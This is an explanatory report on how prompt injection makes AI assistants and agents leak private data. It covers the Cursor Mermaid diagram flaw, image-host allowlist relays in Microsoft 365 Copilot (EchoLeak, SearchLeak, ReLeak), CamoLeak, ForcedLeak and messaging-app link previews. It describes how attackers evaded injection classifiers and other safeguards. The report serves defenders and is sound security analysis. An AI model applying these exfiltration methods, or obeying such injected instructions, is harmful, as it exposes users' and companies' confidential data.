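A chat window that blocks Markdown images can still load images through another feature. Several coding tools can draw diagrams with Mermaid, a library that converts a short text description into a flowchart. Mermaid diagrams can include images, and if the tool lets Mermaid load them from any address, a diagram can leak data just as a Markdown image can.

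Rehberger found this in Cursor, a popular AI code editor, and describes it in Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE*. He demonstrated stealing the notes Cursor had saved about its user and, separately, API keys from a project file. The user had little chance to notice, because Cursor displayed the finished diagram without typing out a long, suspicious address on the screen.

He reported the leak on 30 June 2025. Cursor resolved it on 7 July and shipped the fix in version 1.3 on 29 July. The flaw also received a CVE number, which identifies it in the public catalogue of software flaws.

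The first fix missed some ways of loading an image through a diagram. A second entry, published on 3 October 2025, covers these. According to NVD's *CVE-2025-61589 Detail*, in the US government's vulnerability database, the problem affected versions up to 1.6, and Cursor fixed it in version 1.7.

*Takedown* (Lee, Kim and colleagues, 2025), a study from KAIST, a South Korean university, found a similar flaw through a more systematic search. The researchers examined eight widely used coding agents, whose names they withheld. They intercepted the messages between the agents and their models, read the source code where it was public, and reverse-engineered some of the closed-source agents. They also checked the special syntax that each agent recognised in a model's output for anything that would load an external resource, and found that one agent's Mermaid renderer did.

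By itself, this flaw exposed only what was already in the agent's context. The team combined it with a second weakness that let the agent read files outside the project folder without asking. In their test, the user had the agent fetch a list of reported issues from a code repository, and one issue contained hostile instructions. The agent read a settings file elsewhere on the computer, found an API key and put it into a diagram. Displaying the diagram sent the key to the team's server.

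Lee and colleagues stole files from anywhere on the computer through four of the eight agents, without the user's approval. The diagram was only one way to send data out, and an agent that can open web pages without approval offers an easier one. When the team reported the diagram flaw, the vendor already had a report from someone else, and has since patched it. Two groups found the flaw at about the same time, which suggests that it wasn't hard to find.

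| Product | Finder | Reported | Fix | Status |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | Rehberger | 8 April 2023 | Content Security Policy allowing four Microsoft hosts | Fixed by 15 June 2023 |
| ChatGPT | Samoilenko, Rehberger | 9 April 2023 | `url_safe` check | Partial fix December 2023, stronger around August 2025 |
| Claude | Rehberger | 12 July 2023 | Image loads only after a click | Closed 26 July 2023 |
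| Azure AI Playground | Rehberger | 24 July 2023 | Sanitiser alters image Markdown | Fixed 13 September 2023 |
| Google Vertex AI | Rehberger | 30 August 2023 | Links and images not rendered | Fix confirmed 19 October 2023 |
| Google Colab | Rehberger | 29 November 2023 | Image leak closed, method not public | Closed January 2024 |
| GitHub Copilot Chat | Rehberger | 25 February 2024 | Markdown images not rendered | Fix confirmed 12 June 2024; rendering disabled again August 2025 |
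| Amp | Rehberger | 14 June 2025 | Method not public | Fixed |
| Cursor (diagrams) | Rehberger | 30 June 2025 | Two rounds of fixes | Version 1.3 (July 2025), completed in 1.7 |
| Continue | VerSprite | 20 August 2025 | Asks before loading external images | Fixed 21 August 2025 |
| CodeGPT | VerSprite | 21 August 2025 | None known | Unpatched at publication |
| HuggingChat | PromptArmor | 1 December 2025 | None known | No response to report |
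| dify | veganmosfet | Published December 2025 | None known | Vulnerable at publication |
| Cline | Rehberger | Published 2025 | None known | Vulnerable at publication |

Rehberger found or helped to find ten of these fourteen cases, so the table partly reflects which products he tested, and nobody has tested a representative sample. The cases are also demonstrations in which researchers stole their own test data or a volunteer's, so they show that the leak worked but not how often criminals have used it.

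### Why the flaw keeps returning

A developer who adds a chat window to a product usually picks an existing Markdown library instead of writing one. Markdown supports images, so the library converts them and the browser loads them. Preventing this takes an extra step, and ordinary testing gives the developer no reason to take it because the images appear as expected. veganmosfet reports often finding that a site's Content Security Policy is missing or badly configured.

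Loading images automatically made sense for most of Markdown's history, because the person writing a document chose its images and had no reason to leak their own data to the server that hosted them. In an AI assistant's response, however, a stranger may have chosen the image.

Developers may also focus on the model instead. Chi points out in *Data exfiltration via Markdown image tags* that careful system prompts and lists of permitted tools don't stop this leak. For example, Google Colab's system prompt told the model not to display images, so someone at Google had evidently seen a problem with them, but Rehberger quickly got the model to write one anyway.

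A company that knows about the flaw still has to fix it everywhere model output appears. After OpenAI added its check to the ChatGPT website, the iPhone and Mac apps still lacked it. In July 2026, more than three years after Rehberger's first report to OpenAI, Spain's national cybersecurity institute, INCIBE, published *CVE-2026-14898* (2026). The entry lists an automatic image leak in OpenAI's Codex desktop app for macOS. PromptArmor has reported another leak, with no known fix, in the log viewer on OpenAI's developer platform.

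Rehberger had anticipated this kind of failure. Drawing on his experience of security work, he wrote about OpenAI's crawler-based check that some developers at a large company won't know a protection exists and so won't use it.

The same thing can happen inside a single app. Mattermost, a workplace messaging program, already restricted Markdown images. But according to GCVE's vulnerability entry *CVE-2026-3472* (June 2026), it failed to apply the restriction to posts in which an AI bot displayed the results of its tools. The developers had evidently understood the risk and written code to deal with it, but that code didn't cover a new type of message.

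New features can also make old leaks more serious. When Rehberger reported the Colab leak in November 2023, exploiting it required persuading a user to paste in hostile text, and he considered the severity low. He reported it immediately because he expected Google to start feeding the contents of notebooks to the model. An attacker could then deliver instructions inside a notebook, since people share notebooks and open ones written by strangers. Google began feeding notebook contents to the model in 2024, a few months after fixing the leak.

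OpenAI gave ChatGPT access to past conversations and saved memories while some known ways around `url_safe` still worked. The same leak that could expose the current chat could now also expose details from earlier ones.

Vendors have varied widely in how quickly they fixed the flaw. Continue's developers took a day, Anthropic two weeks and GitHub fifteen weeks, while OpenAI took eight months to release a partial fix. Some of that difference is technical, since a small extension is easier to change than ChatGPT. But a vendor can turn off external images fairly quickly if it is willing to go without them for a while, so much of the delay was probably due to priorities.

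Vendors have also been inconsistent about paying for reports. Google fixed both the Vertex AI and Colab flaws but paid Rehberger only for the Vertex AI report. Willison (2025) noted that Google listed data theft through prompt injection as a known issue in Antigravity, its AI code editor. The company was working on a fix but would not pay for further reports. Several vendors in the KAIST study dismissed some of the findings as intended behaviour. Lee and colleagues attribute this largely to the user starting the task that leads to the attack, which put the findings outside the vendors' rules for security reports. These were tasks developers do every day, such as searching the web or downloading somebody's code.

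## Why did lists of trusted image hosts fail?

Microsoft's 2023 fix for Bing Chat relied on an allowlist, which permitted four Microsoft hosts and blocked all others. Browsers enforce such lists reliably, but they check only the host they are about to contact. If that host forwards the request to another server, the browser can't stop it.

Many ordinary services fetch other web addresses on request. A translation site fetches the page a visitor wants to read, and a messaging app fetches a page to make a preview of it. If a host on an assistant's allowlist runs such a service, called a relay, a hijacked assistant can write an image address at that host that contains the attacker's address and the private data. The browser contacts the permitted host, which then sends the data to the attacker.

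An allowlist can also go out of date. If a company stops paying for a domain that is still on its list, anyone can buy the domain. The browser will then load images from the new owner.

A redirect is a reply that points the browser to a different address. Redirects are more dangerous when a developer enforces the allowlist in the app's own code than when a Content Security Policy enforces it. Under a policy, the browser checks the new host before following the redirect. The app's code may check only the first address and then let a networking library follow any redirects without checking them.

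The best-documented failures are in Microsoft 365 Copilot, Microsoft's assistant for office work. Researchers reported leaks in June 2025, June 2026 and December 2026. Each time, at least one leak sent data to the attacker by loading an image through a permitted Microsoft service.

### EchoLeak

Copilot answers a question by first retrieving related material from the user's mailbox, files, SharePoint sites and Teams chats. Outsiders can't use a company's Copilot, but they can email its employees. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) describes how Ravia's team at Aim Labs, Aim Security's research group, used a single email to steal data from Copilot's context. When an employee later asked a work question that led Copilot to retrieve the email, Copilot followed the instructions in it.

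The attack worked only if Copilot retrieved the email as relevant to the question. Ravia's team therefore wrote a long email covering many common office topics, and Copilot retrieved it for questions on various subjects. Ravia doesn't give a success rate.

Microsoft had four defences in the way, and the team got past all of them.

The first was a classifier, a separate model meant to catch injected instructions in incoming text before they reach Copilot. The team wrote the email as if its instructions were for the employee who received it, and never mentioned AI. The classifier let it through. Such emails are hard to catch because people can word a request to a colleague and a request to an assistant identically. According to Ravia, developers also lack good collections of real injections to train a classifier on.

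The second defence removed links to external sites from Copilot's answers, but the filter missed some of the ways to write a link in Markdown. The team could therefore leak data if the user clicked a link.

The third defence, which blocked external images, had the same gap and failed too, because Copilot used the same filter for images as for links. Microsoft therefore had one fewer independent defence than it seemed to have.

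The fourth defence, the Content Security Policy, blocked images from the attacker's own server. But Copilot's list of permitted image hosts was much longer than Bing Chat's. The version Ravia published has 29 distinct entries, including 11 wildcards, which cover every subdomain of a domain. One wildcard covered all of SharePoint, where any customer can set up a site at its own subdomain, so an attacker could get a permitted host by becoming a customer.

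The team searched the permitted domains for a relay. They first found one in a SharePoint feature that fetches outside content to embed in a page, but it worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. They then found a Microsoft Teams service that also acted as a relay and required no action from the victim. Reddy and Gujral identify it as part of the software that makes previews. The browser requested an image from Teams, as the policy allowed, and Teams requested the attacker's address, which contained the data.

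The classifier and the link filter each missed something that Microsoft had built them to catch. The Content Security Policy allowed every image because each came from a host on the list, so a test of whether the browser enforced the policy would have passed.

The employee had little chance of noticing. Copilot normally cites the documents it has used, but the team got it to leave out the hostile email. Reddy and Gujral note that the result looked like an ordinary broken image. As far as Ravia's team knew, administrators had no setting that would have prevented the attack.

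Aim Labs reported the flaw in January 2025, and Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May. Both disclosed it on 11 June as CVE-2025-32711, and Microsoft confirmed that it had affected no customers. Reddy and Gujral mention that Copilot now strips embedded images and the overlooked type of link from incoming external content. They also mention reports of an option to restrict external communication in some contexts. Neither change shortens the list of permitted hosts.

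Ravia calls EchoLeak the first zero-click vulnerability in a major AI application. He qualifies this by saying that in earlier attacks, the user had to direct the chatbot to a hostile page or file, or the attacker could steal only limited kinds of data. Rehberger's 2023 attack on Bing Chat also leaked data through an image without a click, but the user had to have the hostile page open. With EchoLeak, the attacker chose the victim, who only had to use Copilot as usual.

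Ravia also proposes a term for what went wrong inside the model. In an "LLM scope violation", text from an untrusted source gets the model to use trusted data without the user's consent. An email from outside the company should not influence what happens to documents inside it, however the sender phrases the request. He compares this to stack overflows. Programmers were able to build a specific check for those because they had distinguished them from other memory errors. Aim sold a product based on the idea, so Ravia had a commercial reason to promote the term. But the term describes a rule that doesn't depend on recognising suspicious wording, which Microsoft's classifier failed to do.

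### SearchLeak and the streaming race

A year later, researchers got data out of Copilot through a different relay. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes a leak in Copilot Enterprise Search, which searches a company's emails, meetings and files. The victim had to click a link to a genuine Microsoft site. The link's address contained a prompt that made Copilot search the victim's mailbox and write an answer containing an image.

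Microsoft had anticipated dangerous markup in answers. Its safeguard wrapped the answer in an HTML element for computer code, which makes the browser display markup as plain text. But Copilot streams its answers, meaning that the page displays the text while the model is still writing it, and the safeguard ran only at the end:

1. The model starts its answer, and the page adds each piece as it arrives.
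2. One piece contains an image, and the browser immediately requests it.
3. The model finishes writing.
4. The safeguard turns the whole answer into plain text. The image disappears from the page, but the browser has already sent the request.

Programmers call this a race condition, because the result depends on which of two events happens first. The browser's request was much more likely to come first, because it took only a moment to send, while the safeguard had to wait for the rest of the answer.

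Microsoft could easily have missed this in testing. A tester who looked only at the finished answer would have seen harmless text in place of the image and concluded that the safeguard worked. To find the leak, the tester had to watch the browser's network requests while the answer was still arriving.

A complete answer is also simpler to check than a partial one. A chunk of streamed text can end halfway through an image tag, so that neither half looks like an image. A sanitiser that works during streaming has to hold back unfinished markup until enough has arrived to identify it. Varonis recommends checking the text as the page renders it instead of afterwards, which is somewhat slower or takes some extra engineering.

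The streaming race got an image onto the page, but the Content Security Policy still applied and would have blocked a request to the attacker's server. The policy did allow every subdomain of bing.com, though. Bing's search-by-image feature accepts the address of a picture, which Bing's servers then fetch for analysis. The image in Copilot's answer pointed to this feature and gave it an address on the attacker's server. The browser's policy doesn't apply to requests that Bing's servers make.

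Varonis classes the Bing step as server-side request forgery because the attacker got Bing's server to make the request. But the feature is meant to fetch pictures from addresses that users supply, so someone on the Bing team who looked only at Bing might reasonably have seen nothing to fix. Someone on the Copilot team might also have seen no problem with trusting Microsoft's own search engine.

A relay also makes the leak harder to investigate. An employer monitoring its network sees an employee's browser contacting Bing, which looks normal, and the attacker's log shows a visit from Bing. Only Microsoft can see both the browser's request to Bing and Bing's request to the attacker's server.

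In the demonstration, the data was the title of an email. Email titles often contain security codes for logging in to other services. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* points out that these codes often remain valid for several minutes, long enough for an attacker watching the log to use them. Copilot could also search the calendar and any indexed files that the victim had permission to open.

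According to Varonis, the attack needed all three weaknesses: the preloaded prompt, the streaming race and the Bing relay. Fixing any one of them would have stopped it. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), the advisory for CVE-2026-42824, states that the company had fully mitigated the flaw by 4 June 2026 and that nobody had exploited it. The advisory doesn't specify which of the weaknesses Microsoft fixed.

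### How severe was SearchLeak?

The flaw's published ratings differ. Microsoft labels it "Critical", the highest level on its own scale, but gives it a CVSS base score of 6.5, which is medium. Varonis also calls it critical, citing Microsoft's label. The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026) reports a score of 7.5, or high, from the US National Vulnerability Database. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* (2026) gives the same score and explains that the database's analysts assessed the attack as needing no user interaction.

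The Next Web disputes the 7.5 score. It found that the database's entry had the same answers and the same 6.5 score as Microsoft's own record. The database can show a vendor's score alongside one from its own analysts, and the two don't always appear at the same time, so the outlets may have read different scores in the entry or different versions of it.

Whichever number the database settled on, 6.5 reflects user interaction better, because the victim has to click a link and CVSS counts a click as interaction. Microsoft's assumption that the damage stayed within Copilot is more debatable, since the stolen data came from the mailbox and other systems. If the damage extends beyond Copilot, the formula gives 7.4.

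EchoLeak had a much higher score, 9.3, according to The Next Web, although both attacks could have exposed much the same company data.

### ReLeak

Cato Networks, a network security company, bought Aim Security in September 2025, and Aim Labs became Cato AI Labs. On 3 December 2026 the team published a sequel to EchoLeak, *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), which presented three zero-click leaks from Microsoft 365 Copilot. Like EchoLeak, each attack began with an email that the employee didn't have to open. Copilot retrieved the email while answering an ordinary question, and Microsoft's protections against injection stopped none of the attacks.

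The leaks got data out in different ways. In the first, which again used an image and Bing, Copilot put confidential data into an image's address, the employee's browser loaded the image, and Microsoft's servers passed the data to the attacker. *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* (Antipov, 2026) compares this leak with SearchLeak, which had used a similar route through Bing but needed a click.

Varonis published SearchLeak on 15 June, and Cato reported its findings to Microsoft between 29 July and 20 August, so attackers could still send data through Bing at least six weeks after Varonis's report. Microsoft may have stopped SearchLeak by fixing the preloaded prompt or the streaming race but left the relay in place, or Cato may have found another part of Bing that could relay data.

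The second leak used a saved file instead of an image on the page. Copilot can create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files and save them to OneDrive or SharePoint, Microsoft's file storage services. A hijacked Copilot could save a file containing a link with confidential data in its address. Microsoft's servers then requested that address while processing the file in the background. Antipov reports that in Cato's tests the request came one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if nobody opened the file.

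A Content Security Policy can't prevent this, because no browser is involved. Sanitising what the chat window displays doesn't help either. The delay also makes the leak harder to trace, since an investigator who looked for suspicious requests during the conversation would find none.

The third leak used Copilot's code interpreter, which lets the model write and run Python programs, for example to analyse a spreadsheet. The programs run in a sandbox, an environment isolated from other systems. According to Antipov, Microsoft guarantees in its documentation that no network traffic enters or leaves these sandboxes. This is a form of egress control, which restricts the outgoing network requests a system may make. The team broke the isolation and sent data from the program directly to an outside server, so they needed no relay.

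Agents that people build with Microsoft's Agent Builder and Copilot Studio can also use the code interpreter, but Antipov notes that nobody has confirmed the flaws in those agents.

Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, gives a CVE number and a patch date for each leak, and Antipov's account has the same numbers:

| Route | CVE number | Microsoft's patch |
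|---|---|---|
| Images through Bing | CVE-2026-124115 | 15 November 2026 |
| Links in generated files | CVE-2026-124132 | 11 November 2026 |
| Code interpreter | CVE-2026-78501 | 17 September 2026 |

When Faisal wrote, two of the three CVE records were still marked "reserved", meaning that the numbers were set aside but the details were not yet published. The code interpreter flaw's score had risen from 7.4 to 8.6. Changing only the CVSS answer about user interaction can produce exactly that difference, so the scorers may have had the same disagreement as with SearchLeak, though other combinations of answers can also give 7.4.

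Both accounts give only a range for the report dates, so Microsoft's repair times are also ranges. It took 28 to 50 days to fix the code interpreter, 83 to 105 days for the generated files, and 87 to 109 days for the Bing images. The code interpreter flaw was probably the most urgent, because it gave an attacker a direct connection. It may also have been the easiest to fix, because a sandbox that should have no network access has no legitimate traffic to preserve, whereas Bing and the file services have to keep fetching addresses for other purposes.

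Faisal quotes Cato as concluding that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. Cato sells protection for AI systems, so it benefits when customers think Microsoft's protection is inadequate. Still, its main evidence is strong, because the same team started each time with an email from a stranger and got data out in three ways.

Microsoft fixed all three flaws on its own servers before Cato published, so customers had nothing to install. Cato knew of no real attacks or affected customers, but this is only partly reassuring because Cato can't see most Copilot customers' data. Microsoft is in a much better position to check, since its servers handled the requests in the Bing and file routes.

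### The same problem at GitHub and Salesforce

Two leaks from 2025 show that other companies' lists had similar weaknesses.

Omer Mayraz of Legit Security found CamoLeak, a vulnerability in GitHub Copilot Chat. GitHub fetches outside images through its own proxy, Camo, so its Content Security Policy can block every host except GitHub's own. To stop attackers from using the proxy as a relay, GitHub includes in each Camo address a cryptographic signature that only GitHub can produce. A hijacked assistant therefore can't make up a new address with stolen data in it.

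Mayraz avoided the need for new addresses by collecting signed ones in advance, which he could do because GitHub signs the addresses of images that people include in ordinary content. In his demonstration, the selection of prepared images that Copilot displayed revealed material from private code repositories. No single address contained the stolen data, so a filter that searched addresses for secrets would have found nothing.

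GitHub's signatures were a better defence than Microsoft's list of trusted image hosts for Copilot, and they worked as designed. A signature proves that GitHub has approved an address, but an attacker can still leak data through the choice of which approved addresses to load. GitHub closed this channel that August by turning off images in Copilot Chat.

ForcedLeak, an attack that Noma Security published in September 2025, worked without a relay or proxy. It targeted Agentforce, a product for building AI agents that work with a company's customer records in Salesforce. Many companies have a public web form for sales enquiries, and Salesforce stores what people type into it. An attacker could submit an enquiry containing hidden instructions and wait for an employee to ask an agent about it. The agent would then write an image address containing customer data.

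Salesforce's policy allowed images from a domain the company had once owned but whose registration had expired. Noma bought the domain for about five dollars, and the browser then treated Noma's server as a trusted host. Salesforce regained control of the domain, and in September 2025 it began enforcing a list of trusted addresses for its agents' output.

This fix replaces the failed allowlist with another one. It is an improvement if someone maintains the list, but the original entry was presumably correct when someone added it. A Content Security Policy gives no warning when a domain changes owners, so the company has to keep track of every domain for as long as it stays on the list.

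### Patching one relay at a time

The account that Ravia published in June 2025 showed that Microsoft's Teams relay had been the problem, but his list of permitted hosts also included many other Microsoft services, among them the search engine Bing. Varonis used Bing in an attack a year later, and Cato then used it again. Microsoft had fixed each reported attack but left Bing on the list, probably because Copilot needs some images from it.

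Patching individual relays is worthwhile because each of these attacks needed several weaknesses at once, so fixing any one of them stops a working attack. Microsoft fixed the flaws before they were published, which may be why there are no known victims. However, patching a relay in Teams doesn't fix those in Bing, where each vulnerable feature needs its own patch.

The number of potential relays is also hard to know. A policy entry names a domain, but a relay is a feature of some service on that domain, and a wildcard can cover many services. Different teams run these services and add features over time. A developer who gives Bing a new way to fetch pictures has no obvious reason to consult the people who maintain Copilot's image policy, and the policy doesn't change when the feature launches.

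Attackers need to find only one relay, and the search is getting easier. According to Antipov, Cato's researchers used AI agents to find the ReLeak flaws. Under the researchers' direction, the agents wrote test scenarios, analysed the cases where Copilot refused, and adjusted their next attempts. Ravia's team had described their search through the permitted domains in 2025 as tedious. An attacker with similar agents could delegate most of that work to them.

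Varonis advises security teams to treat any permitted domain as a possible leak if it fetches addresses that users supply. For Copilot, that means checking what every service on the list can do, and checking again when those services change. A shorter list makes this practical. A vendor could copy the images it needs to a host that only serves stored images and so cannot relay requests elsewhere. Even then, the choice of image can reveal something, as CamoLeak showed, although an attacker would also need a way to see which images the browser requested.

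A perfect list of trusted image hosts would have stopped only one of the three ReLeak routes. Copilot's image policy did not apply to the other two, in which generated files leaked data through Microsoft's background processing and the code interpreter leaked it through its own network connection.

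## How do link previews leak data when nobody clicks?

Messaging apps request a link every time they make a preview of it, even if nobody clicks. If a hijacked agent wrote the link, that request sends the link's server whatever data the agent put in the address. In one of the ReLeak attacks, Microsoft's servers leaked data in a similar way, by requesting a link in a file that nobody had opened.

### How an app makes a preview

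Slack's *Unfurling links in messages*, part of the workplace messaging app's documentation for developers, explains how the process works:

1. A person or an app posts a message that contains a full web address.
2. Slack's servers request the address to find out what kind of content it leads to.
3. If it leads to a web page, Slack searches the page's code for metadata, which the site's owner has written for other software to read. This can include a title, a description and the address of a picture.
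4. Slack shows what it found under the message.

The data leaks when Slack fetches the linked page. According to Slack's help page *Share links and set preview preferences*, a link won't expand if the page lacks the necessary metadata. But Slack has to fetch the page to check for that metadata, so data can leak even if no preview appears, and a bare link doesn't mean that Slack made no request. Users can also remove a preview from a message, but by then Slack has already contacted the site.

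### When people wrote the links

Link previews already had privacy problems before AI agents used messaging apps, though smaller ones. Mysk's *Link Previews* (2020) tested how popular chat apps made previews. Threema, TikTok and WeChat made none. In iMessage and WhatsApp, the sender's app fetched the page and sent the preview along with the message. Slack, Discord, Zoom and several others used their own servers to fetch the page.

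In two apps, which the researchers didn't name, the recipient's phone fetched the page as soon as the message appeared. A stranger could send someone a link and learn the recipient's network address, which gives a rough location. The researchers reported the problem, and by the time they published, one developer had fixed it and the other was still working on it.

If someone shared a private link to a contract or a medical record, a company that made previews on its own servers might copy the document. Slack's servers downloaded up to 50 MB from a link, though Slack said it kept previews for only about 30 minutes. Instagram's servers had no size limit. When the researchers sent one link to a 2.6 GB file, Facebook's servers downloaded about 24.7 GB in total, because several of them fetched the same file. Facebook told the researchers that this was working as intended.

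In all these cases, the risk came mostly from what the link led to or from who made the request. The address contained only what the sender chose to put in it, and few people would put a password in a link to a stranger's website.

Mysk preferred previews made by the sender's app, on the assumption that whoever sends a link trusts it. That assumption fails when the sender is a hijacked agent, which can copy any API keys, emails or customer records in its context into the link's address. Moving the fetch to another device wouldn't help, since the attacker's server receives the same address whether the request comes from Slack or from somebody's phone.

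### Rehberger's warning

Rehberger described this leak in Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (2024), using the example of a Slack chatbot that can read websites. A hostile page could get the chatbot to post a link containing something from earlier in the conversation, and Slack would then request the link. By default, Slack unfurls links posted by apps as well as people. When Rehberger posted a test link, his server logged a request from "Slackbot-LinkExpanding".

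In a note from 21 August, *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, Willison (2024) wrote that he hadn't thought about this kind of leak before. He was already keeping a list of image leaks in chat assistants, so many developers of Slack bots probably hadn't thought about it either.

One of them was Anthropic, which had introduced the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to connect AI models to outside tools, and published example programs called MCP servers. The one for Slack let an agent read and post messages, but it left link previews on. Rehberger reported this on 27 May 2025, nine months after his warning. Anthropic archived the program two days later and doesn't plan to patch it. Rehberger couldn't tell whether his report had prompted the archiving.

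The program was still getting more than 14,000 downloads a week, according to Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory*, so Rehberger published the flaw, with Anthropic's agreement, to let users protect themselves. Users can switch previews off by adding two lines to the code, or move to a server that the product's maker maintains.

The advisory also explains why the sensible precaution of restricting the MCP server to a single private Slack channel fails here. Slack's servers fetch links from private channels too, so a message that only five colleagues can read may still send data to a stranger. An administrator who doesn't know this may think it safe to let the agent post without asking for approval, because the worst outcome appears to be an odd message among colleagues.

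The flaw later received a CVE number. NVD's *CVE-2025-34072 Detail* (2025) lists a severity score of 9.3 out of 10 from the security company VulnCheck. Rehberger had scored it 7.5. VulnCheck counted serious harm to the integrity and availability of other systems, but the entry describes only a data leak, so 9.3 is probably too high.

### PromptArmor's tests

By early 2026, many more people were talking to agents through messaging apps, partly because of OpenClaw, a popular agent that users can reach through apps such as Telegram and Slack. In February, PromptArmor published a warning about link previews, along with a public test site.

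A visitor to the test site gets an agent to post a link to the site in a messaging app. If the app generates a preview, the site records the request, the name of the preview bot and any data in the address. The visitor can then claim that record and report which agent posted the link. People can also report agents that did not trigger a preview. PromptArmor uses both types of report to chart which combinations of agent and app are risky.

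PromptArmor found that OpenClaw in Telegram was exposed by default. In *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*, Apostol names two other susceptible combinations from the results, Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio (Microsoft's tool for building agents) and Slack with certain bots. Apostol also lists Discord and Apple's messaging as affected.

| Agent and app | Finding | Status |
|---|---|---|
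| OpenClaw in Telegram | Previews on by default (PromptArmor) | Users can switch them off; no known change to the default |
| Copilot Studio in Microsoft Teams | Susceptible (Apostol) | No known fix |
| Certain bots in Slack | Susceptible (Apostol) | Depends on each bot's developer |
| Anthropic's MCP server in Slack | Previews left on (Embrace The Red) | Archived without a patch |

The results come from people who chose to visit the site, so they can't show what share of agents is exposed. They also depend on visitors correctly reporting which agent they used and how they had set it up. A "safe" report is especially weak evidence, because the visitor may have turned off previews that are on by default.

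The test also covers only the last part of an attack. It shows that an app will fetch a link an agent has posted, but the visitor asked for that link. A real attacker would first have to hijack the agent, and some agents are much harder to hijack than others. Still, a company can use a setting to change the part that PromptArmor tested.

OpenClaw has since changed its Slack integration, and its documentation now lists link previews as off by default. It also lists a separate setting for media previews but gives no default. Slack's servers stop fetching a link only when both kinds of preview are off, so anyone running OpenClaw in Slack should turn both off explicitly. To turn off link previews in Telegram, users have to add `linkPreview: false` to OpenClaw's configuration file. PromptArmor found that its test site stopped receiving data after this change.

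### Why a Content Security Policy doesn't help

A Content Security Policy restricts only the user's browser, but when Slack unfurls a link, Slack's servers make the request. The data would still leak even if Slack's web app had the strictest possible policy.

Slack's servers can fetch images as well as pages. When a link in one of Rehberger's tests led to an image, three Slack bots requested it, and each request sent the data again.

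An image in a chat window loads when somebody has the window open, but Slack can fetch a link as soon as a message arrives. An agent that posts a report every night could therefore leak data while nobody has Slack open.

Fixes an AI vendor makes to its own chat window don't carry over to Slack. Anthropic stopped Claude's chat window from loading images automatically in 2023, but when Claude posts to Slack, Slack controls how links are handled. A developer who connects an existing agent to a messaging app is adding a second renderer and needs to check that one too.

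### Who should switch previews off?

The agent's developer can do it most easily. An app that posts to Slack sends the text of its message along with some optional settings, and two of those control previews:

`"unfurl_links": false, "unfurl_media": false`

The first covers text pages and the second covers images, video and audio. Slack has to fetch a link to determine which kind it leads to, so the developer has to turn off both.

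The developer also knows that a language model wrote the message after reading text from strangers, and Slack may not have that information. Rehberger argues in Embrace The Red that previews should be off by default for any AI system that posts to a messaging app. A developer who wants some previews could add an allowlist of domains, but it would have the same weaknesses as the lists of trusted image hosts.

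However, a developer can use only the settings that the platform provides. PromptArmor therefore asks messaging apps to give developers control over previews, and asks developers to use that control or pass the choice to their users. It would also like platforms to allow different settings for each chat or channel, so a company could create channels that are safe for messages from language models. Apostol says PromptArmor places responsibility "largely" on the platforms, but PromptArmor's own text doesn't go that far.

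There is still a good case for that stronger view. Turning off previews by default for messages from apps would protect every Slack bot at once, including those whose developers don't know about this leak. It would also cover abandoned programs such as Anthropic's MCP server, which nobody is going to patch. Slack can already distinguish an app's messages from a person's, since it notifies apps when a person posts a link to one of their registered domains but not when another app does.

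The main objection is that a new default would also remove previews from many apps that have nothing to do with language models. A bot that posts news stories, for example, would be less useful until its developer turned previews back on. That seems a minor inconvenience, since the developer would need to change only a line or two. Users would also notice missing previews immediately, whereas nobody notices when a preview leaks data. Facebook accepted a larger loss in 2021 when, according to Mysk, it disabled previews in Messenger and Instagram chats for European users because the feature didn't comply with European rules.

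Slack still leaves previews on by default for apps, but it now suggests in its documentation that developers consider disabling them for messages from a language model, and it links to security guidance about data exfiltration. Anthropic's case suggests that advice alone won't be enough. The company had fixed a closely related leak in its own product two years earlier, yet left previews on in its Slack program.

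### What a workspace administrator can do

Administrators have less direct control. The help page says each user can hide previews, but this only affects what that user sees, and Slack would presumably still fetch the link for everyone else in the channel. Owners and administrators can restrict detailed previews for links to connected apps such as Jira, but this restriction doesn't cover links to an attacker's website.

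Slack administrators' most useful power is deciding which agents to allow. Kemple's *Data & security best practices for agentic Slack apps*, which Slack updated in April 2026, recommends that administrators require approval for every new app and sort the permissions that apps request by risk. The guidance doesn't mention previews, and it gives `chat:write`, the permission to post messages, as an example of a low-risk permission that a company can always allow. This could mislead an administrator who is worried about previews, because an agent with that permission can send data outside the company while previews are on.

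Kemple's example requires approval for permission to read channel history, which would limit the private data an agent can get from Slack. But an agent may get private data from somewhere else, such as a mailbox or the files on a developer's computer, and need Slack only to send it out.

An administrator should therefore ask an agent's vendor whether it turns off both preview settings, and then check. The check takes a few minutes. The administrator can have the agent post a harmless link to a server the company controls, then look in the server's log for a visit from a preview bot. It's worth repeating the check after updates, because a new version of the agent might post messages through different code.

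### Previews that bring hostile text in

Previews can also start an attack by carrying instructions to the model. When a user mentions a link, some agents' software fetches the page and adds its title and description to the model's context. Whoever runs the page controls that text and can put instructions in it. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) used this technique, which they call "implicit prompt injection", to make a test agent leak data. The user may never see the instructions, because a page's description is often in its code but not in what the browser displays.

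Turning off Slack's previews for an agent's messages stops Slack from fetching links that the agent writes, but the agent's own software can still fetch links that other people post. The developer also has to stop that software from opening links the user didn't ask about, or at least keep the pages' metadata out of the model's context.

A single attack can hijack an agent through one link and leak data through another. Someone posts a link in a channel, and the agent's software reads the page's description, which hijacks the agent. The agent then replies with a second link, which the messaging app fetches. Nobody has clicked anything, and to people in the channel, the agent appears to have answered a message with a link.

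## What can go wrong with links the user does click?

Even when automatic fetches are switched off, links can leak data in two ways when a user clicks them. In an outbound leak, a hijacked assistant writes a link containing private data, and clicking it sends that data to the attacker. In an inbound attack, the link opens the assistant with a prompt in the URL, which the product runs as if the user had typed it.

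### Links in the assistant's answer

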